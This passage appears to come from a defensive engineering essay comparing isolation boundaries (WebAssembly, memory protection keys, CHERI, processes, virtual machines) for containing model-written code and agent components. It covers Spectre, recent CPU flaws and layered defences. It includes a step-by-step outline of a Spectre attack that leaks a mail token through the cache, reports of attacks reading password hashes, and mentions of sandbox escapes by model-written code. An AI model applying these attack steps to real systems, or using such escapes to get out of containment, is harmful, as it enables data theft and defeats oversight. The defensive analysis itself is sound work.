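Memory protection keys are the hardest to classify as a hardware or software boundary. Sartakov (2026), in *Complets*, notes that researchers have mostly treated them as a kind of software fault isolation, because a component can change its own access rights unless software prevents it. Arm has announced a successor, POE2, which keeps the permissions in tables that the operating system manages. Components can still switch without entering the kernel, but Sartakov found that they need a short piece of trusted code between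 them, because otherwise one component could jump to any instruction in memory it is allowed to enter. Sartakov's prototype, which ran on Arm's software model of the processor, needs about 75 instructions to switch in one direction.

### The mechanisms side by side

The row on trusted software leaves out the processor and the framework's own host functions because all five mechanisms in the table depend on them. The times come from different machines, so they are only a rough guide.

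| | WebAssembly | Memory protection keys | CHERI | Separate process | Virtual machine |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| What enforces the boundary | Checks from the compiler, plus unmapped pages | A processor register, plus a scan of the code | Limits on pointers, plus switching code | Page tables that the kernel writes | A second set of page tables that the hypervisor writes |
| Trusted software | Runtime, compiler and kernel | Scanner, switching code and kernel | Switching code and operating system | Kernel | Hypervisor, virtual devices and usually the host's kernel |
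| Smallest unit | One block of memory per instance | A page, with 16 tags | A range of bytes | An address space | A whole machine |
| Start-up time | 16 ms with a Python interpreter (Pydantic's figure, Apple M3 Max) | 3.5 to 6.2 µs per page scanned | No comparable figure | 5 ms for a new Monty pool (Pydantic's figure, Apple M3 Max) | Low hundreds of ms for Firecracker |
| One call and return, or message and reply | 7 ns (Intel desktop chip at 2.2 GHz) | 27 ns (Intel server chip at 2.6 GHz) | No comparable figure | 35.3 µs (Radxa board) | 30.9 µs (same board, Airlock) |
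| Typical failure | The compiler omits a check, or a host function mishandles a path | The component changes the register, or gets the kernel to read memory for it | The system leaves a usable pointer where the component can find it | A bug in a permitted system call | A bug in a virtual device |
| Repair | New runtime version, possibly within days | Update to the scanner or kernel | Software update, or a new chip if the design is wrong | Kernel update, sometimes with new processor firmware | Hypervisor update, sometimes with new firmware and a full restart |

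The quality of an implementation can matter as much as the choice of mechanism. The 7-nanosecond WebAssembly call comes from *Isolation Without Taxation*, where the program enters the sandbox through a plain function call. Saving and restoring registers raised the time to 120 nanoseconds. An indirect call took 66 nanoseconds with the paper's method but 1,137 in Lucet's original runtime.

Crossing a boundary is slow mainly when it involves privileged software. *NanoZone* (2025), a system for dividing programs on Arm processors, switches between protected areas in 74 cycles without privileged software and in over 6,100 cycles with it. With 28 areas, only about 2% of switches needed privileged software, but the average still rose to 256 cycles.

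### Ten thousand crossings

Suppose that a task makes 20 model calls of one second each, and that its components cross a boundary 10,000 times. If each crossing takes *c* seconds, the total time is

*T* = 20 + 10,000*c*

| Crossing | Time for each | Time for 10,000 | Added to 20 seconds |
|---|---|---|---|
| WebAssembly call | 7 ns | 0.07 ms | 0.0004% |
| WebAssembly call that saves registers | 120 ns | 1.2 ms | 0.006% |
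| Memory protection key switch | 27 ns | 0.27 ms | 0.001% |
| Message between processes | 35.3 µs | 353 ms | 1.8% |
| Message between virtual machines | 30.9 µs | 309 ms | 1.5% |

Virtual machines are slightly faster than processes here only because Airlock has a fast direct channel for small messages. The slowest option in the table adds about a third of a second to a 20-second task, which few users would notice.

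Crossing time matters when a program crosses the boundary inside a tight loop. Wahbe and colleagues' POSTGRES query made 1.4 million calls, which would add 49 seconds at 35.3 microseconds each, compared with about 10 milliseconds for the fastest WebAssembly call. Firefox had a similar problem when it ran its font library in WebAssembly. In *Isolation Without Taxation*, a page-layout test took 8.2 seconds with Lucet's original calls, 2.0 seconds with plain function calls, and 1.1 seconds without a sandbox. Most of the remaining 0.9 seconds of delay with plain function calls probably came from slower code inside the sandbox.

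Start-up time matters more if the framework creates a new sandbox for every piece of model-written code. By Pydantic's figures, starting 20 sandboxes would take 16 milliseconds with Monty's open pool, 0.3 seconds with Python in Wasmtime, 3.9 seconds with Docker and 30 seconds with a remote sandbox service. Starting the 20 Docker containers would delay the user about 11 times as long as sending 10,000 messages between processes. The framework could reuse one container, but a malicious script could then leave something behind for the next script.

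Companies that run code for many customers also have to consider memory and address space, neither of which is a problem for a laptop with one mail assistant. In Airlock's tests, the supervisor's virtual machine had 1 GB, so a thousand agents with one such machine each would need about a terabyte just for supervisors. Cloudflare instead puts tens of thousands of customers' programs into one process. Such a process can run out of addresses, because V8's heap sandbox reserves 8 GiB of them for each program. Corry and Gupta explain that a Linux process normally has 128 TiB of addresses, enough for at most 16,384 such sandboxes, although most of the reserved addresses use no physical memory.

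### Spectre and secrets in one address space

Putting many components into one process saves time and memory. The main argument against it is Spectre, a class of attacks that researchers disclosed in January 2018. These attacks exploit speculative execution, in which a processor predicts what a program will do next, starts the work early, and discards the results if the prediction is wrong.

Suppose that the summariser shares a process with the mail token, and that a software check stops it from reading past the end of a letter. A simple Spectre attack works like this:

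1. The summariser reads many valid positions in the letter, so the processor comes to predict that the check will pass.
2. It then requests a position far outside the letter, where the token is. Before the check finishes, the processor reads a byte of the token.
3. The processor uses that byte to choose another memory location and loads the contents into its cache, a small store of recently used data.
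4. The check fails and the processor discards the byte, but the loaded data stays in the cache.
5. The summariser times its own memory reads. The location that responds fastest reveals the byte.

The software check worked, because the program never officially received the byte. *Spectre is here to stay* (Mcilroy, Sevcik and colleagues, 2019) explains this with two kinds of state. A program's official state includes its registers and memory. The processor also has hidden state, such as the contents of its cache, and many hidden states can correspond to the same official state. A processor is correct if it always reaches the right official state, but the time it takes also depends on the hidden state. Most containment proofs describe only the official state, so they can hold even if the token leaks.

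McIlroy and colleagues, who worked on V8 at Google, tried to stop these attacks in software and measured the slowdown on Octane, a JavaScript benchmark. Programs took 2.8 times as long with an instruction that blocks speculation after every branch, and 1.52 times as long with a replacement for indirect jumps. Forcing array indexes into range, even during speculation, added 10% to the running time, and a broader version of that method added 19%. None of these defences covered every variant, and an engineer accidentally removed some of the protection by adding an optimisation to V8.

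One variant defeated every software defence considered. It exploits processors that read a memory location before an earlier write to it has finished, and so briefly use an old value. Protecting V8 against it would have required redesigning part of the compiler and auditing the whole runtime, with no guarantee of success. Less precise clocks didn't solve the problem either, because an attacker can repeat and amplify a tiny timing difference until even an imprecise clock can measure it.

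They concluded that, on the processors of the time, untrusted code written in most languages with a timer could read all the memory in its address space. Chrome therefore began putting pages from different sites into separate processes. These reads exploit speculative execution, which can leak memory but cannot permanently change it, so a software boundary can still stop the summariser from altering the log.

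### What hosts of shared processes do in 2026

The 2019 conclusion still holds for ordinary processors. Cloudflare's *Dynamic Process Isolation* (2021) acknowledged that nobody knew of a complete defence against Spectre, whether customers were in isolates, processes, containers or virtual machines. Cloudflare aimed to make attacks too slow and expensive to be worthwhile.

Attacks have since become faster. *Remote-Timer-as-a-Service* (2026), by researchers at Cloudflare and the University of Edinburgh, describes a test on Cloudflare's production service that used only programs the researchers controlled. One program read a secret from another in the same process at up to 12 bits a second, 360 times as fast as earlier attacks on the service. At that rate, it could read a 40-character mail token in under half a minute. Cloudflare found no sign that anyone had used such an attack in the previous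 three years, and it blocked the demonstrated attack before the paper was published.

Cloudflare now combines these defences:

- The clock stands still while a program computes, and programs cannot share memory or run several threads.
- A detector looks for signs of Spectre in processor measurements and moves suspicious programs into separate processes. It previously acted only after a run had finished, which was too late for runs lasting hours.
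- V8's heap sandbox and memory protection keys, which also guard against bugs in V8, block the kind of read that the attack used.
- Each machine runs several copies of the whole runtime, which Cloudflare's documentation calls cordons.

Cloudflare warns that neither the heap sandbox nor the keys fully prevent Spectre. Stopping the clock also has limits, since a program with network access can measure time using a remote server. Removing the summariser's clock, threads and network access would make it harder to attack from, but keeping the token in another process is simpler and safer.

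Formal methods help with the variants that researchers already understand. *SpecIBT* (2026) presents formally verified protection against some powerful variants. *Detecting speculative leaks with compositional semantics* (2026) shows that some leaks arise only when two kinds of speculation interact, so checking each kind separately misses them. Researchers can extend its method to new kinds of speculation, but only after discovering them.

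### How hardware boundaries fail

Moving the token to another process makes a Spectre attack harder but does not rule it out. Digital Trends' *MIT researchers found a new Spectre attack* describes TONTOU, which exploits the short gap between a processor clearing its predictions and next using them. On an older AMD processor, an ordinary program obtained Linux's password hashes in five of ten attempts. The attack read only about five bytes a second, and each attempt took around 18 minutes. AMD released a fix for Linux, while Intel planned no further defences because it considered real attacks too dependent on particular conditions.

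A second attack, Branch Target Reuse, followed in September. *New Spectre v2 Variant Exposes Intel, AMD, Arm CPUs to Data Leaks* (Kovacs, 2026) reports that it targets compilers that generate code while a program runs, which are found in browsers, language runtimes and operating system kernels. TechRadar's *Notorious Spectre CPU vulnerability returns hitting JIT engines via side channel attacks* reports that researchers used it to read a password hash from the Linux kernel on Intel processors. Linux's developers released a software defence.

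Processor makers can also be wrong about which chips a flaw affects. The Hacker News' *Google Cloud Warns Three AMD Turin CPU Flaws Could Leak Data* (2026) covers three flaws that may let a program infer data from other processes or the kernel. AMD disclosed two of them in July 2025 and said its Zen 5 processors were not vulnerable, but later withdrew that statement. Google rates the problem as medium severity, and neither company reported any attacks.

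The repair was slow and complicated. New processor firmware had been available for Linux since September 23, but Debian's stable release still had a vulnerable kernel on November 12. Google told customers to install a patched system and then, after a further update, to stop and start their virtual machines, because an ordinary reboot would not be enough. Google had already blocked attacks between virtual machines, so the remaining risk was inside each one.

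Some chips never get a firmware fix. OpenNET's Russian-language report *Уязвимость в CPU AMD Zen 2, позволяющая повысить привилегии* describes a flaw that could let a virtual machine access its host. AMD fixed its desktop processors but left one line of server processors dependent on operating system workarounds.

Confidential virtual machines have also had security flaws. The Hacker News' *New StackWarp Hardware Flaw Breaks AMD SEV-SNP Protections on Zen 1–5 CPUs* (2026) describes a flaw that lets a hostile host run its own code inside a confidential machine on AMD processors. AMD released fixes in July and October 2025, before researchers published the flaw in January, but fixes for some embedded processors did not arrive until April. Kovacs's *Chipmaker Patch Tuesday* (2026) reports that Intel and AMD disclosed more than 200 vulnerabilities in November, including critical ones in the software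 for Intel's confidential machines.

Physical access defeats some of this protection. In October 2025, researchers from Georgia Tech and Purdue University showed that a device attached to a server's memory could extract information from encrypted data. Intel's *TEE.fail* (2025) says its technology is not meant to prevent such attacks, and SecurityWeek reports that AMD takes the same position. This matters much less to a laptop owner who wants to contain a plugin than to someone who rents a confidential machine because they distrust the company that owns the server.

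### How AI changes the search for flaws

AI makes it easier to search a whole code base for flaws, which affects large programs most because they usually contain more flaws. In the April search of Wasmtime, language models stopped finding new flaws of the same kind after two weeks. This suggests that developers can remove most of the flaws a given method can find in a moderately sized runtime. That is much less plausible for an ordinary Linux kernel, which is far larger and keeps changing.

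A runtime's developers can often publish a fix within days, and Cloudflare installs V8 fixes automatically. Software loses this advantage if operators are slow to update, because AI can help attackers turn a published fix into an attack.

AI can help people find hardware flaws too. Outsiders have less information to work from because processor designs are mostly secret, as Mcilroy and colleagues point out. But attackers can exploit each discovered flaw for longer, since owners may have to wait months for a firmware fix or replace the chip. Faster discovery should therefore favour small software boundaries that update automatically, and weaken the case for relying solely on a large kernel or an old processor.

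However, quick repair does not help against the first use of a flaw. If model-written code finds a new flaw while running, as in the escapes that Abdollahi and colleagues cite, the framework needs another boundary already in place.

### Layers that share a flaw

The case for layers is a matter of probability. If *A* is a successful escape from the first boundary and *B* is an escape from the second, the chance that an attacker gets through both is

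P(*A* and *B*) = P(*A*) × P(*B* | *A*)

Here P(*B* | *A*) is the chance of passing the second boundary after passing the first. An attacker with a 1% chance of defeating each boundary has a 0.01% chance of defeating both if the boundaries fail independently, but still a 1% chance if one flaw defeats both.

Running a WebAssembly summariser inside a process with strict system call rules works well because an attacker would usually need one bug in the WebAssembly compiler and another in the few kernel functions that remain available. Combining a container with seccomp adds less protection because the same kernel enforces both.

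TechRadar's *The AI escape is a red herring*, by the chief executive of the software company Coder, recommends a scoring system that makes such combinations easier to compare. The system scores seven parts of a sandbox, including files, network access and credentials, from 0 to 4. A limit that the component can ignore scores 1, a permanent limit in the kernel scores 3, and removing the resource from the sandbox scores 4. For each part, a combination of products gets the highest score of any product in it.

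Comparing boundaries by score helps find gaps, such as a strong virtual machine that contains the user's passwords. But the scores can be misleading if the boundaries with the highest scores depend on the same kernel, since a single bug could then defeat several of them at once. Most published scores also come from product documentation rather than tests.

Layers on one computer share its processor, so a speculative-execution flaw may cross several of them. To protect a very sensitive token, an operator could remove this shared risk by running the summariser on a separate computer.
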